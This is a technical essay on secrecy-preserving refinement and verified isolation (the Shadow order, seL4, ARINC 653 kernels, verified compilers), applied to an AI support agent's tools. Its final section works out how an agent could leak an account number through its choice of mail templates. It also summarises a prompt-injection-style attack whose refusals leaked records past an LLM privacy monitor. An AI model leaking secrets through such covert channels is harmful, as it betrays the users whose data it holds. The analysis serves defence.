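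Both results are secure, but neither is the rule the developer asked for. Heisel, Pfitzmann and Santen similarly object in *Confidentiality-Preserving Refinement* that the changes are hard to predict and may produce a specification that is hard to implement. Mantel does prove that the operators make the best possible adjustments if the groups are as small as possible. After a refinement the groups may no longer be that small, and he leaves open how to find the smallest ones in practice. An extended version handles several observers at once, which deals with the conflict Jacob found between their requirements.

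### The Shadow order

The other option is to change the definition of refinement itself. Morgan (2006), in *The Shadow Knows*, proposed a relation that preserves the observer's ignorance, and McIver and Morgan later extended it to loops and to protocols with several parties. Their method adds a third component to the state of a program:

```
(v, h, H)      v   the visible variable
               h   the hidden variable
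               H   the shadow: every value that h might still have,
                   given what the observer has seen
```

The observer knows the program's text but can't see h. The actual value of h always belongs to H. If H contains only one value, the observer knows the secret.

An implementation I securely refines a specification S, written S ⊑ I, if the following holds from every starting state:

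```
for every outcome (v', h', H_I) of I,
there is an outcome (v', h', H_S) of S  with  H_S ⊆ H_I
```

The implementation may produce only values that the specification could also produce. In each case, it must leave open to the observer every possibility that the specification would have left open.

McIver and Morgan illustrate this with three small programs, in which v and h can each be 0 or 1:

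| Program | What it does | Outcomes (v, h, H) |
|---|---|---|
| r1 | Chooses v and h independently | All four pairs of v and h, each with the shadow {0,1} |
| r2 | Sets v to 0 and chooses h | (0, 0, {0,1}), (0, 1, {0,1}) |
| r3 | Chooses h and makes v equal to it | (0, 0, {0}), (1, 1, {1}) |

Both outcomes of r2 are also outcomes of r1, so r2 securely refines r1. It removes only a choice about v. For r3 to be a secure refinement, its outcome (0, 0, {0}) would need a matching outcome of r1 with v = 0, h = 0 and a shadow no larger than {0}. The only outcome of r1 with those values has the shadow {0,1}, so r3 doesn't securely refine r1. If we ignored the shadows, r3 would count as a refinement, because r1 can produce both pairs of values. The programmer who used the account digit as a reference introduced the same flaw, with ten possible digits instead of two.

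A secure refinement can also increase the observer's ignorance. Suppose a program runs either h := 0 or h := 1, and the observer can see which. The outcomes are (v, 0, {0}) and (v, 1, {1}). If a single step, written h :∈ {0,1}, instead chooses the value out of sight, the possible values of h are the same but both shadows grow to {0,1}. Replacing the visible choice with the hidden one is a secure refinement, but the reverse isn't.

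A specification can also permit leaks with the statement `reveal E`, which publishes the value of the expression E without changing any variable. If the shadow is {0,1,2}, then `reveal h mod 2` shrinks it to {0,2} when h is even and to {1} when h is odd. An implementation may publish at most this much, so the specification also serves as the declassification policy. This makes the order suitable for components that must release some information, such as the calendar assistant, which needs to reveal its user's free times.

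For McIver and Morgan, an attack succeeds only if it gets something out of the implementation that the specification could not have revealed. Such an attack proves that the derivation contains a mistake, which other people can find by checking it. If the derivation is correct and the company still dislikes what leaks, it has to change the specification.

### What the observer must be allowed to see

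The Shadow order assumes a surprisingly powerful observer. Morgan arrives at this assumption through thought experiments that start from two requirements. Developers need to be able to refine one part of a program without re-examining the rest, and the ordinary refinements of visible variables should remain valid.

Consider a program that copies a secret into v and then overwrites it with an arbitrary bit. It seems that the secret should be safe once the program has finished. But a developer may implement "set v to 0 or 1" by leaving v as it is:

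```
v := h;  v :∈ {0,1}    ⊑    v := h;  v := v
```

The program on the right ends with the secret visible to the observer. If secure refinement never reveals anything new, the program on the left must already have revealed the secret. The refinement order must therefore be defined for an observer who remembers every value v has had, an assumption known as perfect recall.

A similar argument applies to branches:

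```
if h = 0 then v :∈ {0,1} else v :∈ {0,1}
⊑
if h = 0 then v := 0 else v := 1
```

Different developers may refine the first program's two identical branches in different ways. The result can be the second program, which reveals whether h is 0, even though the first program seems to reveal nothing. The observer must therefore be allowed to see which branch runs, and so can also count how often a loop repeats. A loop that counts from 0 up to a hidden number reveals that number, even if the counter itself is hidden.

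Morgan assumes an attacker with a debugger, who can pause the program between any two steps, see which line comes next and read the visible variables. The repair firm has no debugger, so the Shadow order will reject some code that would be safe in practice. But the assumption is more realistic than it sounds, because an outsider can sometimes use response times to estimate how often a loop ran, and a log may preserve a secret that a status field held only briefly.

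Developers can relax the assumption for a block of code if they know that nobody can look inside it. They mark the block as atomic, written 〈〈…〉〉, and the observer then sees only its result. For example, 〈〈v := h; v := 0〉〉 reveals nothing, while the same statements without the brackets reveal h. The deployed system must then hide the intermediate value.

Atomic blocks also restrict developers, who may replace a block's contents only with code that has exactly the same effect, as McIver explains in *The Secret Art of Computer Programming*. If 〈〈h := 0 or h := 1〉〉 makes a choice that nobody can see, refining it to 〈〈h := 0〉〉 would reveal the secret to anyone who reads the code.

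### Components built by different people

A company rarely writes all the software around its agent. One supplier may provide the mail component and another the address directory. Each supplier can check its component against a specification but cannot test it in every system a customer might build. The suppliers therefore need a refinement relation that guarantees that if a component I refines a specification S, any program that contains I refines the same program with S in its place.

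This is a demanding requirement for secrecy. Morgan shows this by trying simpler definitions and finding a context in which each one fails:

| What the definition compares | Two programs that it wrongly relates | Code that runs afterwards | What goes wrong |
|---|---|---|---|
| v and the shadow, each separately | h := 0, and h :∈ {0,1} | v := h | Only the second program can end with v = 1 |
| v, h and the shadow, each separately | h :∈ {0,1}; v := h, and h :∈ {0,1}; v := 1 − h | v := v + h | The first ends with v = 0 or 2, the second always with v = 1 |
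| v and h as a pair, the shadow separately | One reveals h only when v = 0, the other only when v = 1 | If v = 0, choose h again in secret | After the first, h is always secret; after the second, the observer may know it |

The first row shows the risk in a definition that ignores the value of h because the observer can't see it. Another component may publish h later, and then the difference becomes visible.

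The final definition compares v, h and H together. Morgan argues that each construct of the programming language preserves refinement under this definition, so every program built from those constructs does too. He also argues that no simpler definition would work, because whenever the final definition distinguishes two programs, even the simplest definition distinguishes them in some context.

When a protocol has several parties, developers have to check a refinement from each party's point of view, because each can see different variables. McIver and Morgan add an imaginary party called agent X, who sees only what is public. Agent X represents anyone who might turn up later, when the protocol becomes part of a larger system.

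This work lets developers prove a small technique once and use it anywhere. For example, to hide a secret bit h, a program can toss a hidden coin k, publish h ⊕ k and discard k. (⊕ is exclusive or, which gives 0 if two bits are equal and 1 if they differ.) Whichever bit appears, h could still be 0 or 1, so its shadow is unchanged. In the Shadow order, this whole block is equal to a program that does nothing.

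McIver uses this to derive a protocol for sending a secret through two untrusted messengers. The specification is one assignment, r := s, which copies the sender's secret to the receiver. The implementation splits s into two shares whose exclusive or is s, and gives one to each messenger. Either share alone looks random. The receiver combines the shares to recover the secret. The messengers could do the same if they shared what they had, so the specification has to treat them as separate parties who don't collude.

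McIver and Morgan take this much further with the millionaires' problem, in which two people want to find out who is richer without revealing their fortunes. Their solution nests four smaller protocols, and they prove each one separately. The full solution is about 30 lines of code, which they call impenetrable at face value. The proofs have many tiny steps, which makes them tedious for people but suitable for machines. Hoang, McIver and others have since implemented the Shadow semantics in Rodin, the proof tool for Event-B, and applied it to small examples of this kind.

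### When some secrets are more likely than others

The shadow records which values a secret might have, but not how likely they are. Suppose the hidden coin is biased, so that k is 0 with probability 0.6. The published bit then equals the secret 60% of the time. Both values of the secret remain possible, so the Shadow order permits the biased coin, but an observer who sees a 1 has some evidence that the secret is 1. This evidence would add up over many messages about the same secret.

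Heisel and colleagues define a refinement relation that accounts for probabilities. They describe each system together with a "window", the channel through which an outsider observes it. A specification's window lists what the outsider may see, and an implementation's window lists what the system can't hide. Anything the developer forgets to put in the specification's window stays confidential, so omitting something by mistake is safe.

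In their example, a sender and a receiver communicate over an untrusted network. The specification allows the outsider to see only the length of each message. The implementation sends encrypted messages over a network that anyone can read, so its window includes every ciphertext. The outsider sees far more data than in the specification, and the question is whether that data reveals anything about a message beyond its length.

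Their general condition concerns pairs of runs that look the same through the specification's window. When the implementation carries out either run, it must produce any given observation with the same probability. For the encrypted network this becomes:

```
for all messages m and m' of the same length, and every ciphertext c:

P( cipher(m, k) = c )   =   P( cipher(m', k) = c )
```

The biased coin fails this test because the message 1 becomes the ciphertext 1 with probability 0.6, while the message 0 becomes the same ciphertext with probability 0.4. A fair coin passes because both probabilities are 0.5. More generally, if there is exactly one key that turns each message into each ciphertext, choosing all keys with equal probability is enough to pass the test.

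The relation is transitive, so developers can work in several steps. But Santen, Heisel and Pfitzmann, in *Confidentiality-Preserving Refinement is Compositional — Sometimes*, found that the relation doesn't hold in every context. In their counterexample, the specified communication service also sends a constant 0 to a neighbouring component, which displays whatever it receives. The implementation encrypts its messages correctly but sends the neighbour the encryption key instead of the 0. The definition allows this because developers may change how they represent data, and the key counts as a new representation of 0. Outsiders see only ciphertexts when the service runs alone, but they also see the key when it runs alongside its neighbour.

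A further condition, called non-disclosure, also has to hold. The additional view that the neighbour provides must not change the relative probabilities of runs that the specification treats as indistinguishable. Developers can reuse their proof about the service, but they have to check non-disclosure for each new neighbour, which a supplier can't do for customers it doesn't know.

The Shadow order would have rejected this service because it requires the implementation's hidden values to be ones that the specification could have produced, and the key is not 0. This strictness helps make the order safe in any context, but it also prevents developers from changing the representation of variables that other components share.

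### Why one number isn't enough

Two common measures of how much a program leaks are Bayes risk, the probability that the observer's best guess at the secret is wrong, and conditional Shannon entropy, the average number of bits of uncertainty that remain after the observation. Neither gives a refinement relation that is preserved by composition. An implementation can leak no more than its specification by either measure, yet leak more by that measure when each is placed in the same larger program.

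For example, suppose a customer's risk grade h is equally likely to be 0, 1, 2 or 3. Program A publishes whether the grade is odd, and program B publishes whether it is 0. Another component then replaces the grade with a single bit that records whether it was 0, and this bit becomes the secret.

| | Bayes risk for the grade | Entropy of the grade | Bayes risk for the later bit | Entropy of the later bit |
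|---|---|---|---|---|
| Program A (odd or even) | 50% | 1 bit | 25% | 0.5 bits |
| Program B (0 or not) | 50% | 1.19 bits | 0% | 0 bits |

At first, the two programs are equally secure by Bayes risk, so either could replace the other, but B is more secure by entropy. Once the later component has run, however, an observer of B knows the secret for certain, while an observer of A doesn't. If the later component kept only whether the grade was odd, the positions would be reversed. Neither program should therefore count as a refinement of the other, regardless of how they compare on any single measure.

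In *Compositional closure for Bayes Risk in probabilistic noninterference*, McIver, Meinicke and Morgan (2010) show that the order based on Bayes risk is not compositional and identify its compositional closure, the refinement order that makes only the distinctions needed for the comparison to hold in every context. Roughly, an implementation may merge observations that the specification distinguishes, but it may not add new distinctions. Programs A and B are unrelated in this order because B separates 2 from 0 and A doesn't, while A separates 1 from 2 and B doesn't.

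Defining such an order requires more information than an average. *Hidden-Markov Program Algebra with iteration* (McIver, Meinicke and Morgan, 2011) uses a "hyperdistribution", which records how likely each observation is and what the observer would then believe about the secret. For program B, the observer becomes certain that the grade is 0 with probability 1/4, and considers 1, 2 and 3 equally likely with probability 3/4. Entropy and Bayes risk can both be calculated from the hyperdistribution, but neither is enough to reconstruct it.

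The same paper extends the quantitative theory to loops and gives an example in which the final results are identical. Here ÷ means division without a remainder:

```
v := h ÷ 2;  v := v ÷ 2      ⊑      v := h ÷ 4
```

Both programs end with the same v, but the left one also reveals h ÷ 2 while it runs, so an observer with perfect recall can distinguish h = 1 from h = 3. The right program doesn't reveal h ÷ 2, so it refines the left program, but the left program doesn't refine it. If h is equally likely to be 0, 1, 2 or 3, an observer guesses it correctly half the time with the left program and a quarter of the time with the right.

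### Comparing what observers can infer

The Shadow order describes programs by their variables. Comparing runs directly can be more natural for a component that exchanges messages. Alur, Černý and Zdancewic do this for labelled transition systems in *Preserving Secrecy under Refinement*. Moon and Varshney used the same kind of model for tool layers.

The developer states which runs look alike to the observer and which properties should be secret, such as "the account number ends in 7". A property is secret if the observer can never infer from a run whether it is true or false. An implementation preserves secrecy if, for each of its runs, the specification has a run that looks the same and from which the observer could infer at least as much. The implementation may therefore leak a property that the specification already leaks. This makes the relation more flexible than Mantel's, which protects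 one fixed and rather strong property.

Standard verification tools can't check this kind of secrecy directly. Many of them accept properties written in the µ-calculus, a logic for describing how a system may branch over time. Alur and colleagues prove that no formula in that logic expresses secrecy in general. Expressing it would require comparing states equally far along different branches, which µ-calculus formulas can't do.

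They can, however, offer a proof method that works with existing tools. It has two parts:

- Every sequence of visible events in the implementation must also be possible in the specification. This is ordinary trace inclusion.
- The implementation must *simulate* the specification, which means that it can match each of the specification's steps and reach a state with the same secret properties.

Trace inclusion ensures that the observer sees nothing the specification doesn't allow. The simulation, which goes in the opposite direction from the usual one, ensures that the code keeps the runs that hide the secret. Both are needed. The mail component that copies the account digit satisfies trace inclusion but fails the simulation, because when the account number ends in 3, the specification can send the reference 7 and the code can't.

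A component that always sends the reference 0 fails the second test as well, although it is safe and satisfies the definition of secrecy-preserving refinement. The method is sufficient but not necessary, and it works badly for changes that remove visible behaviour, such as narrowing a permission scope. If the company drops the repair firm from the list, the new tool layer can't match the old one's mail to the firm. It would be simpler to narrow the specification first, check that its secrets are still safe, and then use the simulation method to compare the code with the narrower version.

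### When the implementation adds something to observe

Specifications leave out many features of a running system, such as caches, logs and response times. An observer may learn a secret from one of these even if every variable in the specification is safe. *On Compositional Information Flow Aware Refinement* (Baumann, Dam and colleagues, 2021) presents a relation designed for this situation. It lets developers change how data is represented and add state that gives the observer new things to see.

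Their definition is epistemic, meaning it is about knowledge. The abstract model specifies what the observer may learn, including any secrets that the company releases on purpose. A refinement may add new observations as long as the observer learns nothing from them that wasn't already available in the abstract model. For example, the mail component could start keeping a public log of message sizes if the specification already lets the observer work out those sizes.

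One drawback of this flexibility is that the relation doesn't automatically preserve noninterference, because an implementation can introduce secrets that aren't in the abstract model. Suppose a new version of the mail component generates a password for its own database and prints it in the public log. If the password has nothing to do with the account number, the observer learns nothing new about the secrets in the specification, so the refinement can be valid even though it leaks the password. Developers therefore have to add a requirement for each secret they introduce.

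The other drawback is that two pieces of code that each preserve the observer's ignorance may not preserve it when run one after the other. Baumann and colleagues trace this to the freedom to change data and observations, which also let the encryption key leak to a neighbouring component. They restore sequential composition by adding conditions that relate the states before and after each piece. They demonstrate the method on oblivious RAM, a technique that hides which memory locations a program is using.

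### Which relation suits a tool layer

For much of a tool layer, the old remedy of removing visible choices is probably best. References, error messages and refusals seldom need to vary, so the specification can fix them as functions of information the observer already has. This leaves the programmer no freedom to misuse, and the company can keep its ordinary refinement tools. The objection that this forbids parallelism matters less for a single session than for a whole operating system. The company still has to decide what one customer may infer from delays another customer causes.

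When the specification has to leave visible choices open, the Shadow order seems the natural default, especially with several suppliers. It makes pessimistic assumptions about the observer, but it is the only relation here that both gives a simple guarantee for unforeseen contexts and lets the specification release chosen information. If the secret depends on random keys or padding, the company needs the quantitative version, since a biased random number generator would otherwise go unnoticed. The epistemic relation is better suited to the layers below, where the data changes form and new side channels appear. The same team usually controls both sides of an interface there and can prove the extra conditions.

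All of these relations restrict how developers may resolve the choices in a specification, but not how an agent may resolve them while it runs. The support agent, for example, makes such a choice when it picks one of eight templates after reading an account.

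## Carrying a secrecy proof down to component code

A real mail server is much longer than the programs in the previous section, which were only a few lines each. A handful of projects have nevertheless proved secrecy for operating-system kernels, a compiler and small concurrent programs. They give an idea of how much work such proofs take, and of which leaks the researchers had to exclude to finish them.

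### The seL4 kernel

seL4 is a microkernel, the small core of an operating system that shares out memory and processor time and passes messages between programs. In 2013, Murray, Matichuk and colleagues, in *seL4*, presented a machine-checked proof that its 8,830 lines of C prevent programs from learning one another's secrets. As far as they knew, nobody had proved this before for the actual code of a general-purpose kernel.

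They sort the programs above the kernel into partitions and assume that all of these programs are malicious, work together and were written with knowledge of the kernel's code. This is much like assuming that a language model may output anything. Suppose a company puts its mail component in one partition and an auditing program in another. The auditing program may read the mail component's log, but no information may flow from the auditing program to the mail component.

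The result builds on two earlier proofs. Klein, Andronick and colleagues (2009) showed that seL4's C code is an ordinary refinement of an abstract specification, a proof that took about 25 person-years. Sewell and colleagues then proved integrity for the abstract specification in about ten person-months. Programs in seL4 can use a resource only through a capability, a token that names the resource and lists what its holder may do with it. The integrity proof shows that programs change only what their capabilities allow. A companion proof shows that, in suitable configurations, no program's authority grows.

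For confidentiality, Murray and colleagues prove a condition on single steps of the abstract specification:

```
take two reachable states s and t in which
    partition p sees the same things,
    the scheduler is in the same state, and
    the running partition sees the same things, if it may send information to p

then after any step from s and any step from t, p still sees the same things
```

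Researchers call this an unwinding condition, because it reduces a claim about whole runs to a claim about each step. If the auditor is running and p is the mail component, the condition follows from the integrity proof, since the auditor can't change anything in the mail component. The condition is harder to prove for permitted communication. When the mail component notifies the auditor, the kernel has to read some of the auditor's state to deliver the notification, so the team had to show that nothing it reads affects what the mail component can observe afterwards.

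When s and t are the same state, the condition requires every possible outcome of a step to look the same to p, so the specification can't leave open any choice visible to p. A specification that allowed any digit as a mail reference would fail. This is the old remedy of removing visible choices, and it is why the secrecy proof carries over to the C code by ordinary refinement.

The original specification did leave such choices open. In several places the kernel read data in its own memory that the specification left out, and programs could see the result. Adding the missing detail and repairing the earlier proofs took about 23 of the project's 51 person-months. The secrecy proof took another 26, and a new scheduler took two. The finished proof has 27,756 lines, about three for every line of C. Murray and colleagues estimate that working directly on the C code would have taken more than 25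 person-years.

Apart from the scheduler, which gives each partition fixed time slots, the C code needed only one minor change. The team dealt with several leaks by restricting how people may configure the kernel:

- *Interrupts.* The kernel doesn't isolate one partition's device interrupts from another's, so only the timer may interrupt. Device drivers have to keep checking their devices instead.
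- *Deletion.* The kernel destroys an object when someone deletes the last capability to it, so the effect of a deletion depends on who else holds one. The configuration must keep a spare copy of each capability that crosses a boundary, in a place no partition can reach. As a result, nobody can remove a channel between partitions once the system is running.
- *Direct memory access.* Devices that write to memory by themselves bypass the kernel's checks, so this feature must be off.

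The proof also doesn't cover most timing channels. For example, a partition can overrun its time slot by calling the kernel just before the slot ends, and programs that share a processor cache can slow each other down. Murray and colleagues leave these channels to other techniques because the fixes reduce performance, and how much slowdown is acceptable depends on the deployment.

The C proof assumes that the compiler, the hardware, the boot code and 450 lines of assembly are correct. In a later overview of the seL4 proofs, Klein, Andronick and colleagues describe a proof that the kernel's binary correctly implements the C code, which greatly reduces the need to trust the compiler.

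### Adding detail without starting again

The seL4 team proved secrecy for a kernel that already existed. *Refinement-based Specification and Security Analysis of Separation Kernels* (Zhao, Sanán and colleagues, 2017) instead develops a specification in steps and keeps it secure throughout. The specification is for separation kernels, whose main job is to isolate partitions. It starts from ARINC 653, an aviation standard that describes 57 services in more than 100 pages of informal text.

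The unwinding condition has two parts. If a partition is not allowed to send information to d, its steps must leave d's view unchanged ("locally respects"). If it is allowed to send information to d and two states look the same to both of them, the states that result from the partition's step must also look the same to d ("step consistent").

Their top-level specification covers partitions and the messages between them. The next level adds the processes inside each partition, with new variables and new events. To show that this is a refinement, they prove that the old events still do only what the top level allowed, that new events do not change the old variables, and that each refined event still belongs to the same partition. The permitted flows must also stay the same. They then prove the two unwinding conditions again, but only for the new variables. If a refinement adds no variables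 or events, secrecy carries over without further proof.

This saved a lot of work. The top level has 680 lines of specification and 5,200 lines of proof. The second level has about half as much specification but only 1,100 lines of proof. The whole project took 12 person-months.

While attempting the proofs, the team found that the standard itself leaks. They then read the source code of three kernels, VxWorks 653, XtratuM and POK, looking for the same faults:

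| Channel | How information escapes | Where it occurs |
|---|---|---|
| Full queue | The sender can tell whether the receiver has made room | The standard and all three kernels |
| Unchecked port numbers | A partition guesses the number of another's port and uses it | The standard, VxWorks 653 |
| Shared port numbering | The next free number depends on how many ports others have created | VxWorks 653; possible under the standard |
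| Scheduling by activity | Who runs next depends on which partitions are idle | Possible in VxWorks 653 and XtratuM |
| Shared process numbering | The next free number depends on other partitions' processes | Possible under the standard |
| Unchecked process numbers | A partition can name another's process in a service call | The standard, VxWorks 653 |

An agent's tools could easily have the same faults. If the mail component numbers all messages from one counter, any session can work out how many mails the other sessions have sent. Giving each session its own counter is an easy fix, but the leak from the full queue is harder to fix. Zhao and colleagues close it by silently dropping messages when the queue is full, so the sender always gets the same answer. A company whose customers are waiting for mail may prefer to keep the error message and declare the small backward flow of information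 as permitted.

The proofs cover the specification but not the kernels' code. Zhao and colleagues checked the code by hand, so they could find faults in it but not prove that none remained.

### When other programs can watch

The seL4 proof covers only a single processor, and the kernel disables interrupts while it runs. Some long calls can pause to let other programs run, but only at fixed points that the specification includes. With several processors, another program may read shared data at any moment, even between two steps that the specification treats as one.

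Sun, Zhao and colleagues (2025), in *Generalized Security-Preserving Refinement for Concurrent Systems*, illustrate this with three threads (programs running at the same time). Thread 1 may send to thread 2, thread 2 to thread 3, and thread 3 to thread 1. All other messages are forbidden. Each thread can see a counter of attempts to send it a message. In simplified form, the faulty code is:

```
send(id, m):
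    count[id] := count[id] + 1
    if the policy forbids this message:
        count[id] := count[id] − 1
        return
    lock the queue;  add m if there is room;  unlock the queue
```

If thread 2 tries to send to thread 1, the code changes the counter, then rejects the message and restores the counter's old value. This passes a refinement proof that compares only the states before and after the call. But thread 1 can read the counter between the two changes, so thread 2 can signal to it by attempting forbidden messages.

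Ray's spending caps could create the same problem in a tool layer. Suppose the layer counts an email towards a recipient's daily limit before checking the scope, then subtracts it if the scope check refuses the email. If only one email is left under the limit, another session could have its email refused between those two steps and learn that someone had tried to write to the same recipient.

The remedy is for the developer to classify every step of the code either as silent or as the counterpart of one step in the specification, taken by the same thread. Two states of the code must look alike to a thread exactly when the corresponding states of the specification do. The specification has no counter, so raising the code's counter would have to be a silent step, which leaves the specification's state unchanged. The proof fails because thread 1 can see the change in the code.

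In the corrected code, the thread checks the policy first and changes the queue only while holding a lock. These steps are silent because nothing else can read the queue in the meantime. Releasing the lock makes the new message visible and corresponds to the specification's single step of adding a message.

Both steps must belong to the same thread. An earlier method, transparent trace refinement, requires only that when a step of the code changes what someone sees, some step of the specification does so too. Suppose a faulty check lets thread 1 put a message in thread 3's queue. The earlier method could match this with a legitimate message from thread 2, which has the same effect on the queue. Sun and colleagues' method rejects the match because the sender is different.

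They applied it to two systems:

- The first is message passing in the 2019 multicore edition of ARINC 653, which they translated by hand from the standard's pseudocode. The full queue and the unchecked port numbers were both still there. After fixing them, the team proved a 260-line model secure with 953 lines of proof, in four weeks.
- The second is a sealed-bid auction. Bidders may send information to the server, the server to a publisher, and the publisher to the bidders, so nothing about the bids can get back to the bidders except through the publisher. The team also proved that the result stays hidden until the auction closes. The model has 202 lines and the proof 719, and the work took three weeks.

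Fewer than 50 lines of each proof check the additional security conditions, so a team that already has an ordinary refinement proof may be able to prove secrecy with fairly little extra work. Both systems are favourable cases, however, because changes become visible at an obvious point, when a lock is released. The method also forbids visible choices in the specification and doesn't cover timing. In the model, the scheduler's choice of thread doesn't depend on secrets, but a real scheduler's choice might.

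### Getting past the compiler

A program whose source code has been proved to keep a secret can still leak it after compilation, even if the compiler preserves the program's results. Suppose two threads write to the same public variable, and one of them takes longer when a secret bit is 1. The compiled program's timing may determine which thread writes last, and the variable's final value then reveals the bit.

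In *Verifying that a compiler preserves concurrent value-dependent information-flow security*, Sison and Murray (2019) built a compiler that provably avoids this. "Value-dependent" means that whether a piece of data is secret can depend on other data. In their example, a phone has a work mode and a leisure mode, and the current mode determines whether the user's typing is secret. The support agent's "private" state similarly determines whether a mail to the repair firm might carry account data.

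An ordinary compiler proof matches one run of the compiled program with one run of the source. Secrecy concerns pairs of runs, so a direct proof must track four runs at once, two of each program. Sison and Murray replace this with three smaller proofs. The first establishes ordinary refinement. The second shows that two compiled runs that should look alike keep the same pace relative to their source runs and stop together. The third shows that such a pair remains matched after every step. On an earlier example, this approach cut the proof from about 3,600 lines to 2,000.

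The compiler translates a small language with loops and locks into a simple assembly language. To save time, it may keep a copy of a shared variable in a register, but only while a lock prevents other threads from changing the variable. Work on the proof also exposed a bug in the published compiler on which this one is based. That earlier compiler could turn v + (v + 1) into (v + 1) + (v + 1).

The compiler was tried on a model of the Cross Domain Desktop Compositor, a system that lets one person work with several computers of different secrecy levels. The model's two threads have about 150 lines of source code, which compiled to about 250 instructions. The compiler and its proofs take up about 7,000 lines. The compiler is a proof of concept that does not support pointers or arrays, and its security theorem requires source programs that never branch on a secret. The assembly model also leaves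 out processor caches and the reordering of memory operations.

### Checking secrecy at every refinement

All these projects require experts in a proof assistant. *Information Flow Control-by-Construction for an Object-Oriented Language Using Type Modifiers* (Runge, Kittelmann and colleagues, 2022) offers programmers an approach closer to the original refinement calculus. A programmer starts with an empty method and fills it in using 13 refinement rules. Each rule checks the secrecy labels of the data involved, and the tool, CorC, rejects steps that would let secret data reach a public variable.

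Their main example checks the signature on an email. The signing key and the result are secret ("high"), while the email object and the client's public key are public ("low"):

```
   verifySignature(client, email)

⊑  (split into two parts)
   fetch the keys;  check them and record the result

⊑  (assignments)
   pubkey  := client.publicKey           low  to low
   privkey := email.emailSignKey         high to high

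⊑  (branch on a high condition: only high data may change inside)
   if the keys match  then  isVerified := true
                      else  isVerified := false

⊑  (assignment)
   email.isSignatureVerified := isVerified      high to high
```

The rule for branches prevents an indirect leak. If the programmer moved verified mail to a public folder inside the first branch, anyone who could see the folder would learn that the keys matched. CorC would reject that line as soon as the programmer added it.

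Objects need extra care because two parts of a program can refer to the same one. Suppose a program creates a public balance object and then stores it as the secret balance of a bank card. The public reference would still point to the object, so the public and secret parts of the program would share data. The rules forbid this unless the object can't change or no other part of the program has a reference that can be used to change it.

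Runge and colleagues prove that every program built with the rules is well-typed in SIFO, an existing language for secure information flow. CorC can also check the method's functional correctness during construction. The labels are cruder than the Shadow order because they record where a value came from, not what an observer could infer from it. For example, subtracting a secret from itself always gives 0, but the rules would still treat the result as secret. Programmers can release data with an explicit `declassify` expression, which needs human review.

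They implemented their case studies in CorC, but call this a feasibility study and leave user studies for later, so it's unclear how much time the method would save an ordinary programmer.

### The cost for an agent's tools

The full seL4 result took roughly 30 person-years, but a company can reuse it. Murray and colleagues note that a whole copy of Linux can run inside a partition, so existing tools wouldn't need their own proofs to benefit from the isolation. If the mail component and the customer database run in separate partitions with no channel between them, the mail component never receives the account number, so a programmer can't hide one of its digits in a mail reference. The company would have to accept the restrictions, though, including the one on direct memory access, which an ordinary server relies on for its disks and network cards.

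Isolation doesn't help with a component that needs the secret to do its job. That component needs its own proof, so it should be as small as possible. Sun and colleagues' results suggest that specialists can verify a few hundred lines of model in a month, and the effort required may be falling. Language models wrote most of the PocketFlow proof, for example, although it concerned safety properties, which are easier to prove than secrecy.

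| Method | What the proof establishes | Size | What stays unproved |
|---|---|---|---|
| Secrecy proved abstractly, then refined to C (Murray and colleagues) | Partitions learn one another's contents only where the policy allows | 8,830 lines of C | Most timing, hardware, boot code, assembly; the compiler, until the later binary proof |
| Stepwise specification (Zhao and colleagues) | The same, and forbidden events stay hidden | 1,240 lines of specification and supporting theory | Kernel code, compiler, hardware, execution timing |
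| Step-by-step matching of concurrent code (Sun and colleagues) | Information flows between threads only along permitted routes | Models of 260 and 202 lines | Timing, deployed code, compiler, hardware |
| Verified compiler (Sison and Murray) | Compilation preserves value-dependent secrecy and adds no timing leaks at the level of program steps | 150 lines of source, 250 instructions | Caches, memory reordering, other hardware behaviour |
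| Construction by labelled rules (Runge and colleagues) | The finished program obeys its secrecy labels, apart from explicit releases | One method at a time; 12 lines in the email example | Timing, compiler, hardware |

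## Limiting disclosure by an agent that reads secrets

All of those proofs concern code that somebody can read in advance. While it runs, a language model also makes choices that nobody has written down. Once the model has read a secret, any choice that an outsider can see may depend on that secret.

### Leaking through permitted choices

Ordinary refinement lets a programmer implement a free choice between v := 0 and v := 1 as v := h, which reveals the secret bit h. The Shadow order rejects this implementation before the program runs.

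Suppose the company deliberately lets the model choose v. The model might set v to h on some tickets, and there is no line v := h to check. If the model may output anything, as containment verification assumes, we have to consider the worst case, in which it leaks h. A correct tool layer doesn't prevent the leak, because it only carries out a choice that the scope permits.

The support agent chooses among 4 addresses and 8 templates, so each mail can take 32 forms. Someone who sees all the mail can learn up to log₂ 32 = 5 bits from each one. If account numbers have 16 random digits, then:

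```
log₂ 10¹⁶ ≈ 53.2 bits          53.2 / 5 ≈ 10.6          so 11 mails are enough
```

The repair firm sees only the templates sent to its own address, so it learns 3 bits per mail and needs 18 mails. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* gives a general bound of log₂(|D| + 1) bits for one message through a typed interface, where D is the set of permitted messages. For 32 possible mails this is about 5.04 bits, so the number of mails needed is still 11. The delays between mails could carry more information.

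Models can leak in this way without using a secret code. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) describes an attacker who fills a shared page with true and false records about someone, then asks an agent with access to the real records to clean it up. The agent refuses to delete some of the records, and its refusals show which ones are true. Against an agent using live Gmail and Notion accounts, this attack revealed 34.7% of the items, even though a language model was checking the agent's actions for privacy violations. A mandatory check on every write and share call, run outside the agent's conversation, reduced this to zero. That check uses a model to compare the proposed output with the protected records, so it does not prove that nothing leaks.

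Reviewing a tool's code before installing it doesn't solve the problem either. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a mail tool that always calls `send_email(body)`, with instructions in plain English that tell the model how to write the body. One version of the instructions specifies a fixed template and another tells the model to copy in a password, but the code is identical in both. The paper proves that if a reviewer's evidence looks the same for a safe version and a leaking one, the reviewer can't soundly exempt either from checks at run time.

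For the leak to happen, the model must read the secret and then make a choice that the outsider can see. The company can interrupt this in three ways, or limit how much gets through:

- *Keep the secret from the model.* Other software handles the account number, and the model receives only a placeholder. It then has nothing to encode, but it also can't do work that requires understanding the secret.
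- *Block visible actions after the model has read the secret.* The support agent's "private" state does this for mail to the repair firm. Eisenach, George and colleagues (2026), in *L3M*, apply the idea more broadly in an agent runtime, where no process that can read private data may also send it. A container that opens private source code has no network access, and neither does any later step of the same plan.
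- *Fix the visible actions beforehand.* If someone chooses the recipient and template before the model reads the account, the choice can't depend on the account number. The agent then can't adapt its mail to what it finds.
- *Accept a limited leak.* A cap of two mails per session limits the leak to about 10 bits, which leaves nearly 10 trillion possible account numbers.

The last option is risky because six sessions about the same customer would be enough to send the whole number. The company therefore has to count the bits for each secret rather than for each session. A cap also doesn't protect very small secrets, such as whether a customer is behind on payments, which is a single bit that one mail can reveal.

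### Labels that follow the data

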